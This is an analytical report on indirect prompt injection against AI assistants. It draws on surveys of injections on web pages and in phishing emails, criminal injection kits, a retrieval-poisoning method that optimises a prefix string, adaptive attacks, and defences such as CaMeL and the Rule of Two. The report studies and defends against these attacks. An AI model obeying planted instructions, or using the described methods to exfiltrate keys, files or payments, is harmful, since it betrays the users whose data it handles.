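Three large surveys cover injections on web pages, which assistants read when they search the web. Google published one in April 2026, using Common Crawl, a public archive of monthly snapshots of two to three billion pages each. Google first searched for phrases common in injections, but most of the matches came from articles about prompt injection. It then had Gemini judge whether each passage belonged to the page's own text or looked out of place, and people checked the results.

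Among the real injections, Google found pranks, requests to add useful context to summaries, attempts to promote a business, and attempts to keep AI systems away. A small number were meant to steal data or delete files on a user's machine, but these mostly looked like experiments by individual website owners. Google saw little sign of the more advanced theft techniques that researchers had published in 2025. The malicious category grew by 32 percent between November 2025 and February 2026, but Google published no counts, so it could have grown from a very small base.

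Khodayari, Acharya and Zhang (2026) counted prompt injections on the web in *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*. They searched the pages at 1.2 billion addresses from the October 2025 Common Crawl for 3,963 phrases and manually reviewed the matches. They confirmed 12,075 injections on 9,676 pages, or about one page in 124,000. They found more through two search engines that index internet-connected servers, which brought the total to 15,387. The table shows what the injections seemed to be for. The shares add up to more than 100 percent because some injections had several purposes.

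| Apparent purpose | Injections | Share |
|---|---|---|
| Disrupt the AI system, mostly by making it produce garbage | 8,894 | 58% |
| Protect personal information or copyrighted text | 4,093 | 27% |
| Reveal whether a visitor is an AI bot | 3,096 | 20% |
| Unclear | 2,632 | 17% |
| Promote a product, source or person | 1,521 | 10% |
| Extract data | 13 | 0.1% |

Nine of the 13 attempts to extract data targeted a system prompt, and only four targeted other secrets. A further 48 injections promoted a job candidate, so the recruiter's hidden-text problem does occur in practice, though rarely on public pages.

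Khodayari and colleagues also tested 100 of the injections by asking 13 models to summarize the pages containing them, with each page presented in four formats. The models obeyed in 81 of 5,200 trials, or 1.6 percent. Commercial models such as GPT obeyed in five of 800. The rate was highest, at 3.9 percent, when the researchers reduced the page to plain text, because this removed the formatting that showed the injection was hidden. Document assistants usually receive extracted text too, so the higher figure is more relevant to them. Most of these injections were crude, however, and an attacker targeting a particular product would write a better one.

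The third survey found a larger share of malicious text. *Fooling AI Agents*, published in March 2026 by Palo Alto Networks' research team, Unit 42, classified the injections in the security company's monitoring data. The most common aim was irrelevant output, at 28.6 percent, followed by data destruction at 14.2 percent and getting past AI content moderation at 9.5 percent. In Khodayari and colleagues' collection, destructive commands made up about 1 percent. Much of the gap could be because a security company's data probably contains more suspicious websites than a general archive does.

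Unit 42 found hidden instructions for AI agents to send $5,000 through PayPal. It also found a scam advertisement for "military glasses" with hidden text meant to make an AI reviewer approve it. Unit 42 called this the first such case it had seen, but knew of no confirmed success against a working ad checker. It had little visibility into which injections succeeded, so it rated their severity by what the attacker wanted.

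The purpose of an instruction to an AI can be hard to judge from its text alone. Unit 42's article, for example, begins with a harmless instruction telling AI agents not to follow the commands the article quotes. Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild* reports that another security company, Forcepoint, also found both harmless and malicious injections.

Surveys like these are much better at finding pranks and marketing than targeted theft. A thief who wants one company's files has little reason to post an injection on a public page. An email or shared document is more direct, and neither appears in web archives. Searches for known phrases also miss careful attackers. Aim's EchoLeak email, for instance, read like a note to a colleague and never mentioned AI. Khodayari and colleagues acknowledge that their method can miss injections that are disguised, behind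 logins, or shown only to AI agents.

### Phishing emails and tools for sale

Attackers have also tried injections in email. Mascellino (2026), in *Attackers Hide AI Prompt Injections Inside Phishing Emails*, reports on a campaign that the security company Barracuda described on October 7. The sample email looked like internal correspondence and came from a public-sector domain, which helped it get past filters. Its password-protected attachment led to malware or password theft. Hidden text could make an AI assistant describe the email as legitimate or urgent, which might lead a recipient who had overlooked it to open it.

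Barracuda also described an invoice email with hidden instructions for an AI assistant to add a false task to its summary, asking the employee to change a supplier's payment details. An employee who did so would send the next payment to the attacker. This closely resembles the false Gemini warning that Figueroa described in 2025, but Barracuda presents it as a real-world example. Barracuda did not say how widespread the phishing campaign was, and Mascellino reports no confirmed loss from either email.

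The campaign weakens one part of the skeptic's argument. Phishing may well take less effort than prompt injection, but a criminal who is already sending phishing emails can add a few lines of hidden text to them with almost no extra work. If the injection fails, the email can still fool the recipient.

Other criminals are selling tools for prompt injection. In late July 2026, Proofpoint reported finding advertisements on closed criminal forums for programs that put injections into emails, PDFs, calendar invitations and web pages. Subscriptions started at around $150 a month. *Cybercriminals Turn to Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks* (Underhill, 2026) was one of several articles that covered the research in August.

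The samples were simple. One email contained white text on a white background. One PDF looked like an ordinary nondisclosure agreement but contained an instruction to send all the victim's spreadsheets to an outside address. Proofpoint doubted that an assistant would act on it, because of the instruction's position in the file. The calendar tool put its instructions in what looked like a meeting agenda, and the invitation appeared in the recipient's calendar before they accepted it. FireTail had reported the same weakness in Google Calendar the previous September.

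The advertisements show that criminals have taken up the techniques researchers demonstrated and are aiming at mail, documents and calendars. They don't prove that the advertised tools work. Proofpoint sells email security, so it gains if companies worry about such attacks, but it calls the methods experimental and says it has not seen hidden-text injection used regularly or on a large scale.

### Getting the planted text retrieved

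A criminal can steal data through one of these tools only if the message gets past the spam filter, the assistant reads it, the model obeys it and finds something worth stealing, and there is a way to send the data out. Most research has focused on whether the model obeys. Chang and colleagues point out that many tests made it easy to get the message read, for example by having the user ask about the latest email. An assistant that searches a large store of files may pick five items out of millions, and the attacker's text has to be among them.

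In January 2026 they tested this step on 11 standard document collections of about 26,000 to 8.8 million items each. They chose 100 questions per collection, planted one malicious item for each question, and checked whether it was among the top five search results. The planted text told the model to answer "Yes" to everything, and the search never retrieved this text on its own.

This is how embedding search should behave, since a text about answering "Yes" has little in common with a question about, say, travel expenses. Chang and colleagues got around this by putting a short string of words in front of the instructions, chosen only to raise the similarity score. If *q* is the question, *D* the instructions, *x* the added string and *E* the embedding, the attacker wants the *x* that gives the highest value of

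f(x) = sim(E(q), E(x + D))

where x + D is the two texts joined together and *sim* measures how closely two embeddings point in the same direction. The planted item reaches the top five if this value is higher than the score of the fifth-best genuine item.

Their program finds such a string by generating thousands of random ones, scoring them, keeping the best fifth and making the next batch more like those. The attacker needs access to the embedding model but not to the victim's documents. In seven of the collections, the search returned the planted item almost every time with strings of five to ten tokens. In two harder collections, the strings had to be about 15 tokens long for typical retrieval rates to exceed 80 percent. Building a string for one question cost as little as $0.21.

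The attack's success depended on how well the genuine documents answered the question, and the size of the collection made no visible difference. In the largest collection, the fifth-best genuine item had an average similarity of 0.75 when the attack succeeded and as much as 0.82 when it failed. A company with many good documents on a subject is therefore somewhat harder to attack through questions about that subject.

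Chang and colleagues also tried a complete attack on a team of AI agents running on GPT-4o, an OpenAI model since replaced by newer ones. A user asked for a summary of emails on a common subject. In about 80 percent of trials, one planted email made the agents send out the user's SSH keys, which give access to other computers. The agents could run programs on the user's machine, which an ordinary document assistant can't do.

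An attacker using this method has to guess what someone will ask, because each string is built for one question. The attacker also needs a good idea of which embedding model the product uses. Strings built with a small Qwen model worked only 10 percent of the time against OpenAI's model, although strings built with OpenAI's model worked an average of 74 percent of the time across the models tested.

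However, planted text is "never retrieved" only when it has nothing to do with the question, so the barrier is lower than it sounds. Martin and Yeung got Gemini to retrieve their file by mentioning bananas in its title, and Aim covered common office subjects in one long email. In Chang and colleagues' tests, repeating the question in front of the instructions also helped, though on one collection it worked only about 20 percent of the time.

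Many requests also involve no search. When a recruiter uploads a résumé, or an employee clicks a button to summarize the email on the screen, the assistant reads exactly what a stranger sent. The need for a malicious document to be retrieved therefore protects people searching a large archive much better than people summarizing an email they have just opened.

Because email costs little to send, an attacker can also make up for a high failure rate at most of these steps by sending more messages. Suppose a criminal sends an injection to 10,000 employees whose companies use the same assistant. Spam filters stop half of the messages, one in ten of the remaining employees makes a request that brings the message into the context, and the model follows the injected instructions one time in 20. That leaves 25 successful injections, but none of them sends data to the criminal if the vendor has closed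 every outward channel.

### What "no known exploitation" can show

Vendors often say, as with Copilot, that they know of no exploitation of a flaw. This is weak evidence that no attack happened if the vendor was unlikely to notice one. The injected message stays in the victim's mailbox, but the victim may have no reason to look at it. Only the attacker's server is sure to have a record of the stolen data arriving, and a company that discovers a leaked client list will probably suspect a stolen password first.

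Criminals are also trying to leave less evidence. The calendar invitation that Proofpoint examined included an instruction for the assistant to delete the prompt after sending the data. The PDF with the hidden instruction produced no warnings on VirusTotal, which checks files with many antivirus programs, because its only harmful content was a sentence of text.

Recommendation poisoning is much easier to detect than theft. The whole prompt is in the link, usually with words such as "remember" and "trusted source", and Microsoft gives customers ready-made searches that find these links in their email and Teams messages. This helps explain why the best-documented real cases are marketing. Theft could be rarer, or just harder to detect.

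The lack of reports still limits how much theft there can have been. Suppose that investigators trace and publicize only one theft in 100, and that each case is independent. The chance of hearing about none of them would be 0.99 multiplied by itself once for each theft:

| Actual thefts | Chance of no public report |
|---|---|
| 10 | 90% |
| 100 | 37% |
| 300 | 5% |
| 1,000 | 0.004% |

On that assumption, a few dozen thefts could easily have gone unnoticed, but a thousand would almost certainly have produced at least one report. If investigators publicized one theft in ten, even 30 thefts would probably have produced one. Nobody knows the real rate, and it could be far below one in 100 for attacks that leave almost no trace. But thieves usually have to use what they steal, such as by selling it or demanding a ransom, which gives victims and investigators another chance to notice the theft.

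The skeptic is probably right that theft through assistants has been rare so far, and the criminal forums provide some independent evidence. Proofpoint found sellers there testing whether an assistant would read a line in a PDF. If such theft had been routine by July 2026, Proofpoint would probably have found them boasting of results instead.

That is weaker evidence about the next few years. Google expects attacks to become more common and more sophisticated, because assistants can now do more for whoever controls them and criminals can use AI agents to automate attacks. Proofpoint expects companies to encounter the advertised techniques within months. Neither company quantifies its prediction, but Barracuda described the phishing campaign about ten weeks after Proofpoint made its prediction.

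## Can models, filters and product design stop it?

Those predictions depend partly on how often injections will work. If models learn to ignore strangers' instructions, criminals will have little reason to keep trying, and much of the disagreement over how seriously to take prompt injection will fade. Models have improved a great deal, at least on the tests their makers publish.

### Success rates for recent models

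Anthropic publishes unusually detailed results in its system cards, which describe how it tested each new model. The table gives figures from several cards, as reported by The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*, VentureBeat, Digital Applied (2026) and The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*. Gray Swan is a security firm that tests AI models.

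| Model | Test | Attempts | Attack success rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.5 | Gray Swan, strong attacks | 1 | 4.7% |
| | | 10 | 33.6% |
| | | 100 | 63% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Coding | 200 | 0% |
| | Operating a computer through its screen | 1 | 17.8% |
| | | 200 | 78.6% (57.1% with added safeguards) |
| Claude Fable 5 | Coding, attacker adapts | 200 per scenario | 0.41% |
| Claude Opus 5 | Gray Swan, general test | 15 | 2.0% |
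| | Browsing the web | 129 scenarios | 0% |

Most rows in this table come from different tests, so comparing them can exaggerate or hide progress. Two comparisons are fair. On the same Gray Swan test, Opus 4.8 let through 5.5 percent of attacks after 15 attempts, while Opus 5 let through 2.0 percent. In the coding test, attackers succeeded 2.09 percent of the time against Opus 4.8, about five times as often as against Fable 5. In September 2026, Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5.5 reported results similar to or better than Opus 5's on every injection test.

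Resistance to prompt injection doesn't seem to come from a general tendency to refuse malicious requests. In Anthropic's tests of agents, Opus 5.5 refused the smallest share of malicious requests among the models compared. Pogorelec (2026), in *Anthropic's new budget model gets much better at ignoring hidden commands*, reports that the small, cheap Haiku 5.5 refused more malicious computer-use requests than Opus 5.5 but resisted injections less well on a Gray Swan benchmark.

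Whether an attack succeeds depends as much on the task as on the model. Opus 4.6 stopped every attack in the coding test, but when it operated a computer through its screen, an attack usually succeeded within 200 attempts. Most of Haiku 5.5's remaining weakness on the Gray Swan benchmark was also in operating a computer. A document assistant does neither task, so we can't take either figure as the chance that it will obey instructions planted in a PDF.

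In OpenAI's tests, GPT-5.6 rarely failed when the attack came directly through the chat, but failed more often when it came through tools and outside content, which is how a stranger's text reaches a document assistant, according to TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026). Måløy's attack on Word documents still worked after Microsoft upgraded to a newer model.

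### Attackers who can adapt

Testing a model against a fixed set of injections measures its resistance only to existing attacks, but an adaptive attacker changes the attack when it fails. SecurityWeek describes an automated version called Tree of Attacks with Pruning, in which a program writes candidate texts, tries them on the model, discards the failures and develops the promising ones until one works. This method requires no knowledge of the model's internals.

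Google DeepMind tried this attack on its own models in *Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025). Training on examples of injections made Gemini 2.5 harder to attack, but in an email scenario the attack still succeeded 53.6 percent of the time, down from 99.8 percent against Gemini 2.0.

In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) tested 12 published defenses against jailbreaks and prompt injection, using automated search and other methods to design attacks that would beat them. The group included researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind. Most of the defenses had been published with attack success rates near zero, but most failed more than 90 percent of the time in these tests. The researchers also ran a contest in which more than 500 participants together got past every defense.

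The researchers assumed an attacker who knows how the defense works and has plenty of computing time. A criminal emailing a stranger may have neither, and can't see how the stranger's assistant responds. But anyone can subscribe to the same assistant, test injections on their own account, and attack other people only once one works. The assumption is therefore more realistic than it looks, at least for products sold to the public.

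An attacker may not need much computing time either. In *The Framing Gap*, Rahman and Kim (2026) built a small agent that held a fake secret and was told not to send it anywhere except one trusted site. They then asked it to summarize a web page that contained an injection. GPT-4o resisted all ten types of obvious attack in 20 trials each. All 200 attacks failed, so by the usual statistical margin the true success rate is below 2 percent.

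Rahman and Kim then rewrote one of the ten to make the leak look like an ordinary part of the task, or to make the attacker's site look like the trusted one. Across the original and seven rewritten versions, GPT-4o leaked the secret in 40 percent of trials, and two of the versions worked every time. The reassuring margin had covered only chance variation in the model's responses to the same texts, so it gave no information about untried ones.

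Removing the rule about the secret barely changed the results. The obvious attacks still failed, and the rewritten ones succeeded 38 percent of the time instead of 32 percent in that run. If the attack had worked by getting the model to break a rule it would otherwise follow, removing the rule should have raised the success rate much more. Rahman and Kim conclude that the model had mistaken the text for part of its task. This fits Ye and colleagues' finding that models judge where text comes from partly by its style.

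Some of the results favor the defender. Thirteen new pretexts that Rahman and Kim wrote from scratch failed in all 130 trials, so finding an approach that works took more luck or skill than rewording one. All 48 valid trials on ChatGPT itself also failed, though the researchers couldn't tell which of OpenAI's safeguards was responsible. GPT-4o dates from 2024 and the other models they tested were small, so the experiment doesn't show how often Opus 5.5 would fail. It does show that a perfect score on a fixed list guarantees little, and that applies to Opus 5's 129 browser scenarios too.

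### What a small failure rate adds up to

Suppose each poisoned document succeeds with probability *p*, and an attacker sends *n* of them. The chance that all of them fail is (1 − p) multiplied by itself *n* times, so the chance that at least one succeeds is:

1 − (1 − p)^n

| Chance per attempt | 10 attempts | 300 attempts | 10,000 attempts |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1% | 10% | 95% | Over 99.9% |
| 0.1% | 1% | 26% | Over 99.9% |
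| 0.01% | 0.1% | 3% | 63% |

The same failure rate can be tolerable for a customer and bad for a vendor. A bakery that receives ten injections a year, each with a 0.1 percent chance of succeeding, would expect about one success a century. A vendor with a million such customers would expect about 10,000 a year. Willison's remark that 99 percent is a failing grade is therefore right for Microsoft, Google and any company that attackers single out, but harsh for most individual customers.

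The formula assumes that attempts are independent, which they usually aren't. With a 4.7 percent chance per attempt, independent attacks on Opus 4.5 would have succeeded 38 percent of the time within ten attempts and 99 percent within 100, but Gray Swan measured 33.6 and 63 percent. For Opus 4.6 operating a computer, independent attempts would have reached a 78.6 percent success rate after about eight tries, but the attackers needed 200. This is probably because some scenarios are much harder to attack than others, and an attacker who has failed many times at a hard one will probably fail again.

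Repeating one text causes a similar problem. Suppose a criminal sends the same injection to 300 employees of different companies, all using the same assistant, and the average success rate is 1 percent. The model might obey at random, one time in 100, or one text in 100 might fool it every time while the rest never do. Either way, the criminal can expect three successes per campaign. But in the first case nearly every campaign catches somebody, while in the second, 99 campaigns in 100 catch nobody and the other catches all 300 people. The average understates the vendor's risk in the second case, because the vendor would see a long quiet period before a very damaging attack.

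An attacker who varies the text can succeed more often than the formula predicts. Rahman and Kim wrote five paraphrases of one successful attack, and their success rates ranged from 0 to 100 percent, with an average of 52. If every attempt had an independent 52 percent chance, an attacker would have a 77 percent chance of succeeding within two tries and 89 percent within three. The actual figures were 82 and 96 percent, because an attacker who switches to a new paraphrase after each failure doesn't retry one that works poorly. Five paraphrases are a small sample, but the reasoning applies to anyone who has several different texts to try.

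Attackers learn from their failures, which raises *p* over time, but vendors can block a text for every customer once they notice it. The formula shows why a low success rate isn't enough by itself, but forecasting would also require knowing how varied the attacks are and how quickly the vendor reacts.

### Microsoft's filters and fixed rules

Microsoft designs its assistants assuming that some injections will succeed. It uses both probabilistic defenses, which make an attack less likely to work, and deterministic ones, which guarantee that a particular attack can't work whatever the model does. It prefers deterministic defenses but still uses both kinds because it considers reliable detection of injections an open research problem.

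The first probabilistic layer is in the prompt. Microsoft tells the model not to obey instructions in outside text, and a technique it calls Spotlighting makes that text easier to recognize. The software can put random markers before and after a stranger's email, insert a special character between all the words, or convert the whole text to base64, which the model has to decode. None of these methods forces the model to treat the text as data, the way a parameterized query forces a database to. Spotlighting was one of the 12 defenses that Nasr and colleagues defeated.

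The next layer is a filter, such as Microsoft's Prompt Shields. It is a classifier, a smaller model trained on known injections in several languages, and the application can block whatever the classifier flags. Google protects Gemini with similar layers and adds reminders to keep the model on the user's task.

A filter can be very good at catching familiar attacks. In Rahman and Kim's experiment, a separate detector flagged every rewritten attack and no harmless page. But the researchers had written those attacks to fool the agent. An attacker who knew about the detector would have written them to fool both, as Aim did with EchoLeak.

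Microsoft applies its fixed rules after the model. A company can label its most sensitive files so that Copilot will not summarize them, and Copilot is supposed to block images and links that could carry data out. Microsoft says it blocked the image technique that Johann Rehberger reported, along with similar ones.

An example with invented numbers shows why a company would want both kinds of defense. Out of 10,000 injected emails, a filter that catches 95 percent lets 500 through. If the model ignores 99 percent of those, it obeys five. If every outward channel is closed, none of the five sends anything out. Because the filter and the model stop all but five of the emails, far fewer attacks could exploit a gap in the rule that closes those channels.

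The multiplication is too optimistic, however, because the layers don't fail independently. An email that reads like ordinary office correspondence is more likely both to get past the filter and to make the model follow the instructions in it. The fixed rule is also only as good as the list it relies on, as the repeated leaks from Copilot showed.

Rahman and Kim tested two rules for outgoing data. The first searched what the agent was sending for the secret, and it failed completely against a simple encoding that they had deliberately left out when designing the rule. The second checked only where the data was going and allowed a single exact address, and nothing got past it. A site with a similar name could fool the model but not a program that compares addresses letter by letter. Real products need many more addresses, and each one may lead somewhere else, so developers can't expect the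 same perfect score. Checking destinations is still more manageable, because a developer can review a list of addresses but can't list every way to disguise a client's name.

Microsoft is also working on TaskTracker, which checks the model's internal activity, rather than the text, for signs that the model has drifted from the user's task. In another project, Microsoft invited people to attack an email assistant's defenses, and more than 800 took part. It has published the roughly 370,000 prompts they produced, which gives other researchers a much better collection of adaptive attacks to train and test against.

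### The Agents Rule of Two

If filters and models will sometimes fail, a developer can make failure less harmful by limiting what the assistant is able to do. Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* is a simple way to decide on the limits. Within one session, an agent should do no more than two of these:

- process input that an outsider may have written
- reach private data or sensitive systems
- change anything or communicate with the outside

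If the task needs all three, Meta's rule is that the agent shouldn't run without human supervision or some other reliable check.

An email assistant that reads incoming mail, searches old messages and sends replies has all three. Its developer could let it read only messages from colleagues, but then it couldn't help with mail from customers, and a colleague might unknowingly forward a document containing an injection. The developer could instead let it research the web without access to the mailbox. OpenAI offers something like this in its Atlas browser, whose agent has a "logged-out mode" without access to the user's accounts. Or the assistant could read everything and write drafts but leave the sending to the user, as long as the drafts don't load external images.

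The third choice limits most office work the least, which may be why so many products began that way. It doesn't protect against a false summary, though, because the user may still act on it.

Willison objected to the "safe" label that Meta's original diagram gave to the combination of outside input and the power to change things. An agent with no access to private data can still delete a shared calendar or post something embarrassing. Meta changed the label to "lower risk".

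An assistant's memory can carry text from one session to the next, but the rule applies to one session at a time, on the assumption that each starts clean. If an assistant saves a planted instruction on Monday, Tuesday's session may contain an outsider's text even if the user opens only internal files. A developer who relies on the rule would have to clear the memory between sessions or treat everything in it as untrusted.

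### One email request through CaMeL

The Rule of Two forbids combining all three abilities. *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues, 2025) describes CaMeL, a system that is meant to allow all three while controlling how data moves between them. CaMeL comes from Google, Google DeepMind and the Swiss university ETH Zurich. It uses two language models and an interpreter, an ordinary program that runs code one step at a time.

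Suppose a user asks the assistant to send Bob the document he requested at the last meeting, and the details are in a shared notes file. CaMeL handles the request like this:

1. A "privileged" model reads the user's request but not the notes. It writes a short program: find the notes, get Bob's address and the document's name from them, fetch the document, send it to that address.
2. The interpreter runs the program. To get the address and the name, it gives the notes to a "quarantined" model, which has no tools and can return only the two values.
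3. The interpreter attaches a label to each value. The label records where the value came from and who is allowed to read it.
4. Before the email goes out, the interpreter compares the labels with a security policy. For example, the policy may let a document go only to people who already have permission to read it, and require the user's approval otherwise.

Suppose an attacker has edited the notes to include an instruction to forward the user's mailbox. The instruction may completely fool the quarantined model, but that model can't forward anything. The privileged model never receives the instruction, and the program has no step for forwarding mail.

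A cleverer attacker would replace Bob's address with their own and leave the program unchanged. The first two steps would work as designed and, on their own, deliver the document to the attacker. Willison's Dual LLM pattern from 2023, which also kept a model with tools away from untrusted text, had this weakness. CaMeL catches the attack at the fourth step because the document's label doesn't list the attacker as a reader. These labels are a version of the capabilities that Hardy wanted after the compiler overwrote the billing file, because permission is attached to the data instead of depending on which program handles it.

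Debenedetti and colleagues tested CaMeL on AgentDojo, a set of simulated office, banking, travel and chat tasks for AI agents. CaMeL completed 77 percent of the tasks with its guarantees in place, compared with 84 percent for an unprotected agent. It also used almost three times as much text, which makes each request slower and more expensive. Rahman and Kim tried a simpler split between a model that plans and a model that reads. It stopped every leak in their test and kept 90 percent of the agent's usefulness, though on a much narrower task.

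A drop of seven percentage points in completed tasks seems acceptable for a company that handles medical or legal records. But the average doesn't show which tasks fail. CaMeL has to take its plan from the user's request, so it has trouble with requests like "do whatever the customer asks for in this email", where the plan is in the untrusted text. Many people want an agent for requests of that kind.

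CaMeL also doesn't protect the content of an answer. If a user asks for a summary of an email, the quarantined model writes the summary, and an injection can still make it false. The researchers leave such attacks out of scope because they don't change which actions the system takes or where data goes. With the halved financial figures, a label could at least warn the reader that the numbers had passed through a model that was also reading a file from the web.

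Somebody also has to write the policies. Loose policies let data out, while overly strict ones make the system keep asking the user, so that security depends on the user's answers.

### Approval and fatigue

Nearly every design here relies on the user at some point. Meta's rule requires supervision when an agent has all three abilities, and CaMeL requires the user's approval for actions its policy would otherwise block. Microsoft counts user consent as its last layer of defense. For example, Copilot in Outlook can draft an email, but the user has to approve the text and send it. ChatGPT's agent pauses before a purchase. On sensitive sites, such as a bank's, the user has to keep the page open and watch, and the agent stops if they switch to another tab.

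The best measurement of how well this works comes from Anthropic's experiment with paid testers. Users like them would approve an attacker's dangerous command 86 percent of the time on the first request. If each decision were independent, they would approve at least one of two requests 98 percent of the time.

The testers' behavior makes sense given what they had seen. An agent that asks for permission 40 times a day makes 10,000 requests over a working year of 250 days. If one of them is malicious, a person who approves everything without reading is right 99.99 percent of the time and saves hours of work. Warning text can't change that calculation much, because a request would still rarely matter.

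Asking users for approval less often should help. Sending an email is a natural point to ask, since people are used to reading a message before it goes out and send emails far less often than they open files. The question should also include the information the user needs to decide. "Allow this action?" is nearly useless, while "Send the client list to an address that came from a supplier's PDF?" would alarm most people. A system that tracks where data came from, as CaMeL does, could ask the second question. It is reasonable to expect people to make better decisions with such questions, but no one seems to have measured the improvement in document tools.

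Approval also has to come before the action, but Notion's assistant asked for permission after the browser had already sent the data. And approval only protects against actions the user can judge, so it doesn't help when hidden text has slightly raised a résumé's score.

OpenAI also advises users to make narrow requests. An agent told to "review my emails and take whatever action is needed" has no clear task to help it recognize when something is wrong, and it has more reason to open a bank statement than an agent told to find the date of Thursday's meeting. OpenAI says that narrow requests make attacks harder but do not rule them out.

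### Can anyone solve it completely?

Model developers don't promise a complete solution. OpenAI called prompt injection a "hard, open problem" in November 2025 and compared it to web scams. A month later, according to The Decoder, it acknowledged that the problem may never be fully solved. Microsoft calls the risk inherent in how language models work. David C reached much the same view by comparing prompt injection with SQL injection.

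The Decoder nonetheless suggested in July 2026 that Opus 5 "may have solved" injection for browser agents. The two positions conflict less than they appear to, because people use "solved" in different ways. A browser agent that resists every attack in a good adaptive test may be safe enough for most of its users. But an engineer who has to guarantee that a hospital's records will never leak can't rely on a test result, and needs a rule that holds even when the model follows an attacker's instructions.

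OpenAI has described its goal as an agent as trustworthy as a security-conscious colleague. This is probably achievable, and recent models may already be harder to fool than many employees. But that standard may be too low for a product, because a text that fools a widely used model can fool it in every company at the same time, not just once in one office, as when a colleague falls for a trick.

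The strict designs can guarantee protection against particular kinds of harm, but each gives up something that vendors advertise. If an assistant blocks outside images, its answers can't show a chart from a supplier's website. If it keeps private data separate from the web, it can't compare a company's own contract prices with today's market prices in one step. The user would have to run the web search in one session, save the result, and open it in a second session that has the contract but no way to send anything out. CaMeL can allow such combinations, but it doesn't allow a plan to change based on what a stranger's email says.

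Agents that work overnight are the hardest case. Suppose a company wants an agent to answer customers' emails while the staff are asleep. The agent has to read strangers' text, look up private records and send replies without anyone's approval. No design described here would fully allow that. The company could follow the rule David C recommends and give the agent only the privileges of whoever wrote the email, so that it can open only that customer's orders and reply only to the address on file. An injection could still produce a rude or mistaken reply, but the only private data it could send would be the customer's own. The agent also could not issue refunds or forward difficult complaints to suppliers, so those would have to wait until morning.
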